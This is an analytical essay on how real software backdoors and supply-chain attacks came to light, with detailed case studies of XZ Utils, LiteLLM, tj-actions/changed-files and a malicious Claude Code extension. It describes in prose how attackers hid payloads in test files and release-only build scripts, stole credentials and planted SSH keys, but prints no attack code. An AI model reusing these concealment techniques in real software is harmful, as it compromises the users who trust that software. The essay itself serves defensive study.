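# How concealed software backdoors were discovered, and what that implies for checking AI-written code

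## What a concealed backdoor is and how one can come to light

A concealed backdoor is a deliberately hidden function or weakness that gives access or an advantage to anyone who knows about it. *ROSA* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and colleagues, 2025) compares it to an unprotected but concealed entrance in a fortified castle, whose walls keep out everyone except the few people who know where the entrance is. Backdoors can be in ordinary program code, a processor, the mathematics of a cipher or the data used to train a machine-learning model. Most cases in the later sections involve program code, and a few involve cryptography.

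In 1974 a US Air Force report on the Multics operating system described how someone could add a "trap door" to an innocent system function, so that one very unlikely input would give access to the machine's protected memory. Russ Cox, in *Fifty Years of Open Source Software Supply Chain Security*, compares that report with the backdoor that a developer found in the compression software XZ Utils in March 2024. There too, a very unlikely input let an attacker run commands on the machine. How people found such backdoors is relevant to checking AI-written code, particularly to deciding how much effort should go into reading the code and how much into watching what happens when it runs.

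### Backdoors, mistakes and malware

People use the word "backdoor" loosely, and Zdziarski (2016) notes in *Backdoor* that no technical definition has won wide agreement. Zdziarski proposes three tests (intent, consent and access), all of which a mechanism must meet to count as a backdoor. Thomas and Francillon, in *Backdoors*, break a backdoor down into an input source, a trigger, a payload and a privileged state. In one D-Link router, for example, the input source was the network connection and the trigger was a particular string of text in the field where a web browser identifies itself. The payload was a jump past the password check, and the privileged state was that of a legitimate, logged-in user.

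A backdoor differs from an accidental vulnerability in that it is intentional. Thomas and Francillon express this by comparing the actual program with the developer's and the user's understanding of it. Both kinds of flaw exist in the program, but the developer knows about a backdoor and the user does not, while neither knows about an accidental vulnerability.

Nobody can directly inspect how the developer pictured the program. Where the code contains an explicit path from trigger to payload, such as a comparison with a fixed secret password, Thomas and Francillon consider the intent clear. All eleven real-world backdoors in their main comparison were of this kind. But a developer can also plant something that looks like a bug and exploit it later. Thomas and Francillon call this a deniable backdoor, and technical evidence alone cannot distinguish it from a mistake. GitHub's *2020 State of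 the Octoverse* (2021) calls these "bugdoors". Investigators then have to rely on circumstantial evidence about who made the change, when, and whether it had any legitimate purpose. Thomas and Francillon concede that such arguments rest on human intuition and do not amount to proof.

Base rates also make it harder to judge whether a flaw was deliberate. GitHub, which hosts a large share of the world's open-source projects, took a random sample of 521 security advisories and found that 17% concerned explicitly malicious behaviour. Among the alerts it sent to developers about flaws in components they used, the share was 0.2%. On these figures, which date from 2020, a reviewer who finds a dangerous flaw in a popular package should expect it to be an honest mistake. That expectation helps a well-made bugdoor pass as a mistake, and GitHub's figures would also have counted it as one.

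Competent analysts can examine the same software and disagree about whether it contains a backdoor. In January 2025 the US cybersecurity agency CISA examined the firmware, or built-in software, of a hospital patient monitor. CISA's *Contec CMS8000 Contains a Backdoor* describes a hidden function with a hard-coded internet address in every version the agency analysed. The security company Claroty later studied the firmware, and its *Do the CONTEC CMS8000 Patient Monitors Contain a Chinese Backdoor?* concludes that the function is "most likely not a hidden backdoor" but the result of insecure design. According to SecurityWeek, Claroty does not regard the function as hidden. Both consider the device dangerous, but they disagree about whether the function was concealed and what it was for, and the firmware alone does not settle either question.

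Ordinary malware, such as ransomware, is harmful as a whole, and nobody who understood it would install it. A backdoor sits inside a program that people want and that still does its job, and it usually stays inactive until it receives an input that only someone who knows about it would supply. Some cases fall between the two. In 2018 researchers found that event-stream, a JavaScript package, contained code that harvested bitcoin wallets once a particular mobile app had included it. The code needed no secret input, but it was hidden in a component that developers trusted. This was a supply-chain attack, which reaches its victims through software they obtain from a trusted supplier. Finding such code is much the same problem as finding a backdoor in the narrow sense, so the later sections include both.

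### From the author to the running program

A new line of code in an open-source program passes through several stages before it affects anyone, and attackers have interfered at nearly all of them. SLSA, an industry specification for supply-chain security, is based on the resulting concern that the code people run may not be the code someone checked.

The developer first commits the line to the repository, the shared store of every version of the source and a record of each change. A source reviewer, human or machine, can see the line, its date and the account that submitted it, but not who was using the account. Even so, code is easiest to review at this stage. Ohm, Plate and colleagues (2020) observe in *Backstabber's Knife Collection* that malicious code in a repository is more accessible to review than an attack on the build system or on the registry that distributes packages.

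At the review stage, someone other than the author reads the change. The reviewer can see what the line appears to do and ask why the program needs it, but rarely sees the code of the dependencies, the outside components the program relies on. Cox counts 1,581 packages behind kubelet, a fairly small low-level program in the Kubernetes system for running software on many machines. Readers also miss many flaws that nobody tried to hide. GitHub found that vulnerabilities often went undetected for more than four years before disclosure.

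When a project publishes a version, a maintainer packages the source into a release archive, which can differ from the repository. In the XZ Utils attack, Cox writes, the critical lines that set the backdoor in motion during the build were only in the archive, so a reviewer could have read every commit in the repository without seeing them.

The build then turns the source into a program that a computer can run. It depends on compilers, scripts and servers, none of which appear in the source under review. At the software company SolarWinds, attackers compromised the build platform and installed an implant that injected malicious behaviour during each build.

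In *Reflections on Trusting Trust*, Thompson (1984) described altering a compiler, the program that translates source code into machine instructions, so that it would add a secret password whenever it translated the Unix login program. Anyone who read the compiler's source would soon have noticed this change, so Thompson added a second one that made the compiler reinsert both changes whenever it translated its own source. Thompson could then delete both changes from the source, and the login program would keep its backdoor "with no trace in source anywhere".

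The build produces the binary, which is the compiled program. Reviewing source code shows nothing about a binary unless someone can show that the binary came from that source. *Reproducible Builds and Insights from an Independent Verifier for Arch Linux* (2025) points out that most users and companies never compile open-source software themselves, so secure source code is not enough to protect them. An analyst can reverse-engineer a binary, using its machine instructions to work out what the program does, but this is slow work for experts. Checking a binary takes less work with reproducible builds. *Lila* (2026) describes them as the practice of ensuring that given source, in a defined environment, always produces a bit-for-bit identical binary, which lets outsiders rebuild the program and compare the results.

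In practice, the comparison often fails for mundane reasons, such as a timestamp in the output. In *No Snake Oil*, Dietrich, White and colleagues (2026) tried to rebuild 10,449 popular releases of Python packages with two automated tools. One tool produced a package for 68.0% of the releases and the other for 56.5%, but only 15.4% and 19.1% of those packages, respectively, were byte-for-byte identical to the published ones. Most of the differences were in files that describe the package, not in its program code. Among the rebuilds whose source matched, a more tolerant comparison established equivalence for 60.2% and 78.9%. For now, then, a mismatch is weak evidence of tampering in a Python package. A match shows that the binary corresponds to the source, but the source itself could still contain a backdoor.

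Finally, the program runs on a particular machine alongside other software. A source reviewer can only predict what will happen there. Behavioural monitoring records what a program or an AI agent does as it runs, such as its processor use and its system calls, which are requests to the operating system to do things like open a file or start another program. Infrastructure monitoring covers the surroundings, such as networks, accounts, build servers and repositories. A backdoor can hardly do anything useful without leaving traces when it runs. Kokkonis and colleagues report in *ROSA* that all 17 backdoors in their test collection changed the pattern of system calls when triggered.

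A concealed backdoor is hard to detect because its trigger may never fire while the program is being observed. Ohm and colleagues note that code that runs only under certain conditions is harder to detect in test environments, because the testers may not know or meet those conditions. Fuzzing, which means running a program on many automatically generated inputs and recording unusual behaviour, can sometimes find the trigger on its own. But fuzzing tools traditionally detect crashes, and a well-coded backdoor should not cause one.

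### Three ways into open-source projects

*Not In My Git Yard* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli, 2026), which introduces the detection tool Lily, sorts known attacks on open-source projects by the point at which the backdoor entered.

Malicious commits place a backdoor in the project's own repository, when a maintainer accepts a harmful contribution or attackers push one from a compromised account. In 2021, for example, attackers breached the PHP programming language's server and committed a backdoor, then a change that appeared to fix the problem, and then a change that undid the fix. These commits left traces in the version history, and the backdoor was detected before the code reached an official release.

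Attackers can add a backdoor to a released package without changing the source repository. In 2010 and 2011, attackers compromised the servers that distributed two file-transfer programs, ProFTPD and vsFTPd, and for several days people who downloaded the official packages received a backdoor with them. The infected vsFTPd release differed from the previous official one by 1,407 lines in five files. The new function that gave the attackers access was only 23 lines long, so even someone comparing the two releases would have had to search for it.

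A compromised dependency carries a backdoor into the other projects that use it. XZ Utils, for example, contained a backdoor that became active only when the package was used by OpenSSH, the standard software for logging in to remote machines.

These categories can overlap. The XZ attackers also worked through the repository and the release archive, so that case involves all three. The categories don't cover closed products, where the supplier may have planted the backdoor itself without having to get it past a maintainer. SLSA lists the malicious producer among its threats but offers no solution for closed-source software.

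### First sign and confirmation

Seven routes of discovery, alone or in combination, account for the cases in the later sections:

- Performance or malfunction: someone notices that a program is slow, crashes or otherwise misbehaves.
- Automated alarms: a scanner or monitoring system flags a package, an account or an action.
- Integrity checks: a comparison of two copies, or of one copy with its recorded checksum or signature, reveals an unauthorised change.
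- External cryptanalysis: people outside the body that designed a cipher or random-number generator study its mathematics and find a weakness.
- Leaks: an insider talks, or confidential documents become public.
- Incident forensics: investigators reconstruct a break-in or malfunction from logs, memory and files, and trace it back to the software.
- Source review: a person or a machine reads the program text and finds something that should not be there.

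Discovering a backdoor usually takes more than one step, and different steps can come from different routes. The first sign is the observation that makes someone start looking, and confirmation is the step that establishes that a backdoor is present. In the XZ Utils case, the first sign was that a login program used more processor time than normal. Many harmless faults also slow a program down, so this didn't prove there was a backdoor. A closer investigation confirmed it by finding the backdoor in the compression library.

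Thomas and Francillon set a demanding standard for confirming a backdoor. An analyst must recover the trigger, the payload and the path that connects them, and must also show that the construct was part of the developer's design. This last requirement is again a question of intent, and it can remain open after analysts have settled every technical question. Leaks are such valuable evidence partly because a document or a witness can state the developer's purpose, which is seldom clear from the code.

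Separating the first sign of a backdoor from its confirmation also makes it possible to count discoveries fairly. Reading code is a common way to confirm a suspicion, even when something else raised it. Counting confirmations would therefore overstate how often source review first detects backdoors, while counting first signs would credit whatever prompted the reading.

The cases are well documented publicly and vary in how people made the discovery, but they are not a representative sample. Much larger collections have the same weakness. The Atlantic Council's *Breaking trust* covers 115 publicly reported supply-chain attacks and vulnerability disclosures from a ten-year period. It describes these as a "consistent but not random sample", says they probably undercount attacks on some high-value targets, and draws no conclusions about frequency. A handful of cases picked for their variety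 can show that a way of finding backdoors has worked and what it required, but not how often it works. The cases also include only backdoors that somebody found. After discussing the luck involved in the XZ discovery, Cox says "perhaps we have missed others".

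## XZ Utils, 2024: slow logins on a test machine

XZ Utils is a free set of file-compression tools that most Linux systems include. Its core is liblzma, a library of code that other programs load when they need it. In early 2024, two versions of liblzma contained a backdoor that let the holder of a particular cryptographic key run commands on a machine without logging in. Andres Freund, a Microsoft engineer who works on the PostgreSQL database, found it while working on something else. He announced the discovery on a public security mailing list on 29 March, in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise* (Freund, 2024).

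The backdoor targeted remote logins over SSH, which most Linux servers handle with sshd, a program in OpenSSH. OpenSSH does not use liblzma itself, but Debian, Fedora and several other distributions (projects that package Linux with thousands of other programs) modify sshd so that it can report to systemd, which starts and supervises services. The modified sshd loads a systemd library, which loads liblzma.

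*How NixOS and reproducible builds could have detected the xz backdoor* (Malka, 2025) explains the last step. A Linux feature called ifunc lets a library run some of its own code while a program is starting, normally to pick the version of a function that suits the machine. The backdoor used ifunc to replace a function that sshd uses to check login keys. Reading all of OpenSSH's own source would not have revealed the backdoor.

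### From a benchmark to the release archive

Freund was measuring a very small difference in PostgreSQL's speed and wanted the test machine as idle as possible. In The Microsoft Threat Intelligence Podcast's *Behind the Scenes of the XZ vuln* (2024), Freund recalls that the machine was not running a graphical desktop, so the processor should have been idle. Yet sshd occasionally used a fair amount of processor time in short bursts. Login attempts by strangers scanning the internet caused these bursts. The attempts failed immediately because the usernames were wrong, so they should have used very little processor time.

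Freund then ran a profiler, a tool that records where a program spends its time. In a comment on the news site LWN that day, Freund reported that much of the time went into liblzma, in code that the profiler could not match to any named function (andresfreund, 2024, *A backdoor in xz*). This was odd, because Freund had installed the files that supply those names. Freund also remembered a warning from Valgrind, a tool that detects improper use of memory, that had appeared in automated PostgreSQL tests a few weeks earlier, after some package updates.

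In the timings Freund posted, a failed login took 0.299 seconds before the backdoored library was installed and 0.807 seconds afterwards. The connecting program used the same processor time in both runs, so the extra half second came from the server. Just starting sshd to print its help text took about 0.5 seconds with the backdoor active and about 0.01 seconds without it. This start-up delay affected every login because recent versions of OpenSSH execute sshd afresh for each connection, as Johnston (2024) explains in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*.

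Many retellings, including Malka's, begin with this half-second delay. On the podcast, Freund accepts the figure but calls that version a myth. Freund noticed the processor use and the strange profile first, then used the timings as a quick check of whether the backdoor was active. The check was needed because the code switched itself off under some debugging tools and when sshd started outside its normal service. The backdoor also appeared in some rebuilds of the library and not in others.

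Freund can't name a single moment when he recognized the backdoor. One strong clue was that the build produced the same file several times with different contents, one of them about 50 kilobytes larger than before. Even then, Freund suspected Debian's package rather than XZ itself, because code from the project's repository did not reproduce the problem. The project's release archives did reproduce it, and they contained a line in a build script that was missing from the repository, which showed that the backdoor came from the XZ project.

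Confirming the backdoor took profiling, debugging and comparing the archive with the repository. When Freund went public, nobody had worked out what input triggered the hidden code. Thomas and Francillon require an analyst to recover the trigger, so by their standard the confirmation was incomplete. It was still enough for Freund to urge people to upgrade immediately.

### Why reviewers missed it

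The bulk of the backdoor was in the public repository, inside compressed files presented as test data. Russ Cox's *Timeline of the xz open source attack* (2024) dates their addition to 23 February 2024. A compression library needs odd and damaged files for its tests, and a note in the same directory, written long before the attack, explained that many of the test files were handmade and had no better source code than the files themselves. A reviewer could see that someone had added the new files but could not read them as code. The one clue was that no test in version 5.6.0 used them. Kekäläinen (2025), in *Could the XZ backdoor have been detected*, argues that the change still looked like ordinary sloppy practice, and that only another XZ developer could have noticed that no matching test followed.

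The instructions for extracting the hidden code and adding it to the library existed only in the release archives. Lasse Collin, the project's original maintainer, confirms this in *xz backdoor* (Larhzu, 2024) and adds that the test files are harmless without those instructions. The instructions were in a modified copy of a standard build file of the kind projects routinely add to their archives. They took effect only when someone built a Debian or Fedora-style package for one common type of processor, so a developer who compiled the archive in the usual way got a library without the hidden code.

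Checking the archive's signature would not have helped either. A contributor called Jia Tan had created and signed both archives, and was authorized to do so as a maintainer.

"Jia Tan" had spent more than two years reaching that position. Cox's timeline starts with a harmless patch in October 2021. During 2022 several accounts, which Cox considers probably fake, complained about slow progress and pressed Collin to hand over control. Collin replied that the project was an unpaid hobby and mentioned long-term mental health problems. Jia Tan could change the repository directly by the end of 2022 and published a first release in March 2023. *Towards Socio-Technical Topology-Aware Adaptive Threat Detection in Software Supply Chains* (Welsh, Finnsson and colleagues, 2025) counts more than 500 patches by Jia Tan across several projects. The early ones appear legitimate. By the time of the attack,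 Jia Tan was one of the two people best placed to review changes to XZ.

### How far the two versions spread

Jia Tan released version 5.6.0 on 24 February 2024 and version 5.6.1 on 9 March. Debian added 5.6.0 to its "unstable" branch, where new packages arrive first, on 26 February and to its "testing" branch on 5 March. Debian moved to 5.6.1 on 27 March. Fedora included the new versions in Rawhide, its development branch, and in the beta of Fedora 40. Arch Linux and NixOS also distributed them, but neither modified sshd in the way the backdoor needed.

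Freund wrote that the distributions with the new versions had mostly put them in pre-release editions. Bruce Schneier's *XZ Utils Backdoor* (2024) puts the discovery weeks before the code would have entered both Debian and Red Hat Linux. On 28 March, the day Freund privately alerted Debian and other distributions, Jia Tan asked Ubuntu to adopt 5.6.1. Debian returned to an older version the same day. In the first days after the disclosure, nobody had seen the attacker use the backdoor.

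### Warnings that looked like ordinary bugs

Someone else saw the backdoor cause errors before Freund did. On 4 March, nine days after the release of 5.6.0, Scott (2024) told Fedora in *Invalid writes regression in liblzma.so* that about 130 of roughly 1,000 tests in a performance-monitoring project had started to fail over a weekend. Valgrind reported that liblzma was writing to memory where it should not.

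Richard Jones, who packaged XZ for Fedora, at first could not reproduce the fault with XZ's own tests. Later that day he reduced it to a program that only loaded the library, and even that produced 112 errors. The error report listed `_get_cpuid`, the function that was the backdoor's entry point, 24 days before Freund alerted the distributions.

Jones treated the problem as a bug. The errors pointed to ifunc, a feature that already had a reputation for causing trouble with Valgrind, and a real ifunc bug in the same release was causing crashes on another distribution. Jones switched ifunc off that afternoon, and the next day Scott confirmed that the tests were passing again. Fedora also told Jia Tan about the errors. On 8 March Jia Tan published a supposed fix, which Cox describes as a misdirection. A day later Jia Tan actually fixed the errors by replacing the test files that contained the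 attack code. Jones recorded the bug as fixed in 5.6.1, and Fedora closed it.

The reports had helped the attacker repair the backdoor. After Freund's announcement, another developer looked at the supposed fix, called it "somewhat plausible" and doubted that it would have seemed suspicious at the time.

The workaround kept the backdoor out of Fedora 40's build of 5.6.0, though Fedora didn't know the backdoor existed. Jones (2024) explained afterwards that the hidden build instructions did not add the backdoor when ifunc was off. Fedora 40 was by then frozen for its beta, so it kept 5.6.0 with the workaround, while Rawhide moved on to 5.6.1 with ifunc on again. Jones also thought it very unlikely that the packagers would have found the code even if they had spent days inspecting the archive.

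### If the backdoor had been faster

According to Freund, the slow step was a search through the symbol tables, the lists of function names and addresses that programs use to find one another's code. The backdoor ran this search whenever sshd started, even if the attacker wasn't connecting, so Freund could notice the delay without knowing how to trigger the backdoor.

The delay was a side effect, though, and another backdoor may not have one large enough to notice. An attacker can also remove side effects, as Jia Tan did with the Valgrind errors within days of hearing about them. Slowness by itself is also poor evidence of an attack, since most slow programs have an innocent explanation. Freund considered several, including missing debugging files, before suspecting an attack.

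Kekäläinen thinks that without the slowdown the backdoor would most likely have stayed hidden for months or years. Nobody can test that, but it is plausible, because by late March the Valgrind errors had a fix and Fedora's packagers had stopped investigating them.

A change in systemd might have limited the damage. On 29 February a developer proposed that systemd's library stop linking to liblzma, and the project accepted the change on 5 March. Cox thinks this would have defeated the attack, and notes speculation that the attacker hurried because of it. The change was one of a series meant to reduce the library's dependencies, and no one has reported a security purpose for it. It would have protected only machines that received the newer systemd, and the attacker might have looked for another route. In late February Jia Tan had also quietly disabled a security restriction in the xz program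 itself, but Cox could not establish why.

### How much of it was luck

*The XZ Backdoor* (2024), a blog post written two days after the announcement, puts the discovery down to "pure luck". Freund's own comment was that it "required a lot of coincidences". The main ones were these:

- Freund's machine ran Debian's unstable branch, which had the new library and a version of sshd that loaded it.
- The machine was receiving login attempts from the internet, which kept starting the slow code.
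- Freund needed an idle machine for the benchmark. On most systems, Freund says, an open web browser would have been enough to hide the bursts.
- Freund had turned off the processor's automatic speed boost to get steadier measurements, which made the bursts last longer.
- Freund knew enough about several layers of the system to interpret the profile, and kept going when the backdoor seemed to vanish.
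- All of this happened before the code reached the stable releases that most servers use.

Some of these conditions mattered less than others. Turning off the speed boost only made the bursts easier to see, and the last condition affected how much harm the discovery prevented, not whether it happened. It also wasn't pure chance that somebody noticed a symptom. The backdoor's defects showed up on other people's machines too, and the performance-monitoring project that alerted Fedora found one of them through routine automated testing. It was less likely that someone who saw a symptom would have the skill and patience to trace it to its cause. Freund sensibly advises other engineers to be curious about anomalies, but few people have time to investigate every one.

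Routine checks might have reduced the dependence on any one person. Comparing each release archive with its repository would have revealed the altered build file, but also many legitimate differences. Kekäläinen found dozens in a later, clean version of XZ, including a generated configuration script of 26,434 lines, and concludes that a diligent Debian packager could not reasonably have spotted the backdoor. A very experienced reader might have noticed that the altered file's version number was too high, or compared the file with copies in other packages, but Kekäläinen considers that comparison an unreasonable amount of work.

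Comparing the release archive with the repository was much more useful once Freund had a reason to do it. In *A backdoor in xz* (2024), mdeslaur argues that the mismatch between the two made the code easy to spot, and that nobody would have noticed it in the repository. In a Debian discussion, *Validating tarballs against git repositories* (2024), Vincent Bernat likewise expected that if Debian had built from the repository, the attacker would have put the part missing from it there. The person who replied was less sure, because more developers build and test from the repository than from the archives, and one of them might have run into a problem earlier.

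For a more selective check, Malka proposes building the library once from the archive and once from the repository, then comparing the results. Harmless differences in documentation or generated scripts should disappear, leaving only those that change the program. The check requires reproducible builds, and XZ was reproducible in all 17 snapshots of the NixOS package collection that Malka tested, from 2017 to 2023. With the backdoor active, the two copies of liblzma differed by 48 kilobytes, close to the growth Freund had noticed.

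But Malka's first attempt on the backdoored version found no difference, because the hidden instructions did nothing in a normal NixOS build. Malka had to set a variable to make the build resemble one of the attacker's targets. The check would have worked if Debian or Fedora had run it on its own packages, but it would have missed a backdoor placed entirely in the repository.

Other proposals involve watching contributors. Nealon (2025), in *Beneath the Mask*, searched the records of XZ and 19 similar projects for relative newcomers who had merged their own changes without anyone else's review. The final search picked out four of the 1,996 people who had proposed changes. One was Jia Tan, with 24 such merges, and the other three appeared to be innocent. Welsh and colleagues found that Jia Tan changed an average of 132 lines per file, against 47 for Collin, and made the final malicious changes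 at unusual hours. Some of Jia Tan's harmless changes also came at unusual hours. Both studies chose their signals knowing who the attacker was, so they don't show how well those signals would identify an unknown attacker. Even a correct match would only have told someone where to look, because the malicious code would still have been hidden in the test files and the archive.

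## Compromised packages of 2025 and 2026: a crash and automated alarms

The XZ attacker spent more than two years earning the right to publish releases. In three later supply-chain attacks, attackers tampered with software that many developers already used, and someone noticed within a day. Two of these attacks included a backdoor in the strict sense. Malicious releases of LiteLLM, a Python library, stole credentials and also installed a service that fetched further instructions from the attackers. A fake copy of the extension for Claude Code, Anthropic's AI coding assistant, was designed to let an attacker log in to developers' computers. The tampered version of tj-actions/changed-files, a component used in automated build jobs, only stole credentials.

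### LiteLLM: a fault that froze a laptop

LiteLLM lets a program use AI models from many providers. Developers install it 15 to 20 million times a week from PyPI, the main public registry of Python packages. On 24 March 2026 attackers uploaded two malicious versions, 1.82.7 and 1.82.8. PyPI's *Incident Report* (2026) traces the attack to an upload credential exposed through a compromised copy of Trivy. According to LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026), the project was using Trivy for security scanning.

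Schaumann (2026) reproduces the public advisory in full in *backdoor in litellm version 1.82.7*. According to the advisory, the code collected login keys, cloud credentials, database passwords and cryptocurrency wallets and sent them to the attackers. It also set up a permanent background service, labelled "System Telemetry Service", that contacted a server for further instructions. This service was the backdoor, because whoever controlled the server could keep directing the machine after the theft. The advisory's one-line summary mentions only the credential theft.

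Version 1.82.8 of LiteLLM contained a file that Python runs automatically every time it starts. Malicious code in the file started another copy of Python, which ran the file again, so the copies kept multiplying. Callum McMahon, an engineer at the AI company FutureSearch, was using a Mac with 48 gigabytes of memory when it began to stutter. According to InfoQ's *PyPI Supply Chain Attack Compromises LiteLLM*, the processor was at 100%, and the tool that lists running programs took tens of seconds to load and then showed about 11,000 processes. McMahon photographed the screen and forced the machine to restart.

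Most of the times below come from FutureSearch's *Catching the LiteLLM PyPI Attack*, which includes McMahon's full session with Claude Code.

| Time (UTC) | Event |
|---|---|
| 10:39 | Version 1.82.7 appears on PyPI |
| 10:52 | Version 1.82.8 appears on PyPI |
| 10:58 | A plug-in in McMahon's code editor, Cursor, downloads 1.82.8 as a dependency |
| 11:07 | The malware creates a file for its permanent service, but the file stays empty |
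| 11:09 | McMahon forces the laptop to restart |
| 11:13 | McMahon starts investigating with Claude Code |
| 11:40 | Claude Code finds the malicious file in the LiteLLM package |
| 11:58 | McMahon confirms that PyPI is still serving the file and emails PyPI's security team |
| 12:00 | McMahon emails LiteLLM's maintainers |
| 12:02 | FutureSearch publishes a warning |
| 12:04 | McMahon shares the warning on Reddit |
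| 12:30 | FutureSearch adds that 1.82.7 is malicious too |
| About 13:11 | PyPI quarantines LiteLLM, so that nobody can install it |

The last time, 13:11, is the time of the first upload plus the 2 hours 32 minutes that PyPI reports as the total exposure, since PyPI gives no clock times. LiteLLM's own figure of about 40 minutes from 10:39 must be wrong, because McMahon downloaded a fresh malicious copy from PyPI at 11:58.

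PyPI counted more than 119,000 downloads of the two versions during the attack. InfoQ reports over 40,000, but PyPI's count is more reliable because it runs the registry. PyPI also estimates that 40 to 50% of LiteLLM installations in that period automatically took the newest version. The rest came from users who had fixed the version in advance. LiteLLM's official Docker image, a ready-to-run copy of its software, was safe because it also used a fixed version. The number of infected machines is unknown, because not every downloaded copy is run and 1.82.7 did nothing until a program loaded it.

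### What the AI assistant contributed

Claude Code misdiagnosed the problem several times before getting it right. McMahon first described the flood of processes, each running a block of encoded text. Claude Code replied that this pattern was "not malware" but a normal way for programming tools to pass code to Python, and suggested that one of its own sessions had got stuck in a loop. It also reported finding nothing that would restart itself after a reboot, although the malware had already created the empty file for its service.

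McMahon then typed in the first few characters of the encoded text from the photograph. They decoded to two ordinary lines of Python, and Claude Code took this as support for its theory. It then connected the crash with an earlier system fault at 1:36 that morning, which McMahon thought was unrelated. Next it suggested that Cursor had failed to clean up old processes during an automatic update, and it recommended turning automatic updates off. A background search of the installed packages for the encoded text found the file 27 minutes into the investigation.

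The early explanations were all reasonable, because most crashes have innocent causes. FutureSearch writes that it took "some healthy skepticism" to get Claude Code to look for malice, since a user is very unlikely to be the first victim of an unknown attack. McMahon supplied that scepticism and insisted on a final check with a fresh download in an isolated container before accusing anyone.

After the discovery, Claude Code was fast and mostly accurate. It explained the malicious file, traced how it had reached the laptop, found where to report it and drafted the public warning. It also noticed that LiteLLM's GitHub repository had no release matching either version. This suggested that someone had uploaded the packages directly to PyPI, so reviewing the repository would have revealed nothing. Other attacks may not leave this clue. Jensen and Wang report in *The attack chain behind the v1.107.0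 LiteLLM release* that LiteLLM's own release pipeline published another compromised version on 21 October.

FutureSearch concludes that developers without security training can now raise the alarm much faster than before. One case is weak evidence, and McMahon knew enough to inspect the running processes and save a picture of them. But the assistant plausibly shortened the work between the crash and the report, which would normally require knowledge of system logs, package caches and containers. AI agents can also cause the problem, and a later section covers a malicious PyPI package that one wrote in 2026.

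### Whether anyone had noticed version 1.82.7

Version 1.82.7 carried the same malware without the fault. Willison (2026), in *Malicious litellm_init.pth in litellm 1.82.8*, explains that the malicious code in this version was in an ordinary program file. It therefore ran only when a program imported the package, not every time Python started, and it did not multiply.

No public record shows that anyone noticed version 1.82.7 before McMahon's report. PyPI received its first report 1 hour 19 minutes after the upload. That was 11:58, when McMahon emailed about 1.82.8, if PyPI counted from the upload of 1.82.7 at 10:39, or 12:11 if it counted from the upload of 1.82.8. Suspicion of 1.82.7 seems to have grown out of the same investigation. While helping McMahon, Claude Code recommended checking 1.82.7 because it too had no matching release on GitHub. FutureSearch's *litellm 1.82.8 Supply Chain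 Attack on PyPI (March 2026)* (2026) confirmed at 12:30 that it was compromised.

Of the two versions of the malware, only the one with the fault, 1.82.8, prompted a report. InfoQ cites the AI researcher Andrej Karpathy's view that without the mistake the malware would have gone unnoticed for much longer. Comparing the two versions gives only limited support for this view, because 1.82.7, which lacked the fault, was the newest release for only 13 minutes before 1.82.8 replaced it. Somebody may also have noticed something odd without reporting it.

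Another case from the same campaign suggests that this malware could be caught without a crash. The attackers also published malicious versions of telnyx, another Python package. PyPI received the first report 1 hour 45 minutes after the upload and quarantined the package after 3 hours 42 minutes. Reports from people PyPI had designated as trusted triggered the quarantine automatically. PyPI has not said what first alerted them, but it works with security researchers who regularly scan its packages. Without the crash, the malicious LiteLLM release might therefore have lasted for hours rather than months, though the attackers would have collected more credentials.

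The attackers, or someone helping them, also tried to obstruct the response. At 13:03 FutureSearch reported that LiteLLM's owner account had closed the public discussion thread about the problem and that hundreds of bots were flooding the thread. FutureSearch thought the attackers had very likely taken over the account. By then McMahon's warning was on FutureSearch's site and on Reddit, where the attackers could not close it.

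### tj-actions/changed-files: an unexpected network connection

GitHub Actions runs automated jobs for software projects, such as building and testing each change. Developers assemble these jobs from ready-made components called actions. One action, tj-actions/changed-files, lists the files that a change affects. More than 23,000 repositories used it in March 2025.

On 14 March an attacker added malicious code to the action and moved its version labels to point to that code. Projects that asked for a version published years earlier received the new code instead, so any earlier review of that version no longer protected them. The action downloaded a script that searched the build machine's memory for passwords and other secrets and printed them in the job's log, which anyone could read if the repository was public. The attack exposed credentials but gave the attacker no continuing access to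 the machine, so it was a theft rather than a backdoor.

Sharma (2025), in *Harden-Runner detection*, reports that the first sign was an unexpected destination in a job's network traffic. Harden-Runner, a product of Sharma's company, StepSecurity, monitors build machines while jobs run.

Network baselining works well on such machines because build jobs are repetitive. A typical job fetches the project's code, downloads its dependencies from a few registries and uploads the result. Over a series of runs, a monitor can record which addresses the job contacts and treat that list as the baseline. If the job later contacts an address that is not on the list, the monitor raises an alert or, under a stricter setting, blocks the connection. Because this check relies only on the job's normal connections, it requires no analysis of the program or prior knowledge of the malicious code.

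The tj-actions case shows why the comparison has to be with the job's own history. The malicious script came from a GitHub service for sharing snippets of text. The service is legitimate and widely used, so a list of known malicious servers would be unlikely to include its address. The connection was suspicious only because these jobs had no reason to make it.

A baseline can't flag the misuse of an address that a job already contacts. A harmless update may also add a new address, so an alert still needs investigation. In this case StepSecurity ran the compromised action in a test repository and watched it download and execute the script. Another developer found the change that had introduced the malicious code. Reading code thus helped confirm the compromise, after the monitor had narrowed the search to one component.

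The public sources give the time of the tampering but not of the alert. Esler (2025), in *tj-action/changed-files GitHub action was compromised*, puts the tampering at 16:57:45 UTC on 14 March. Sharma's post has the same date, so the alert must have come within about seven hours of the tampering if that date is in UTC, or about 14 hours if it is in US Pacific time, though it could have come within minutes.

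StepSecurity sells the monitor, and Sharma's announcement ends by recommending it, so the account needs an outside check. Esler confirmed the compromise on a public security mailing list the next day, reporting that it affected all 361 version labels and describing the same theft of secrets from memory. Esler credited StepSecurity and another security company, Semgrep, with early analysis, but did not say who noticed the attack first or how. The attack is therefore well established, but only StepSecurity's account supports the claim that a network alert revealed it. The early date of Sharma's announcement makes that claim plausible. Sharma gives no figures for false alarms, which anyone deciding whether to rely on such a monitor would want.

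### The Claude Code extension on Cursor's marketplace

McMahon's code editor, Cursor, has a marketplace where users can install extensions. On 29 October 2026, that marketplace served a malicious copy of Anthropic's Claude Code extension from about 2:27 am to 1:35 pm Pacific time, a little over 11 hours. Cursor's *Security notice* estimates that it affected at most 5,000 users. The notice names version 2.1.313, and its Japanese edition, *セキュリティに関するお知らせ*, adds version 2.1.312, neither of which Anthropic had made.

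The extension added the attacker's key to the list of keys that the computer accepts for SSH logins. It also tried to switch on the SSH service and to open a connection to the attacker's server through which the attacker could log in. This was a backdoor in the strict sense, because it gave access to the holder of a particular key. On most computers it did not work, because switching on the service required administrator rights, which the extension usually lacked, and because the code contained errors. But the key remained in place, and Hall (2026) warns in *Official Claude Code Extension Compromise* that the backdoor would work on any Mac whose owner had already turned on remote login or did so later.

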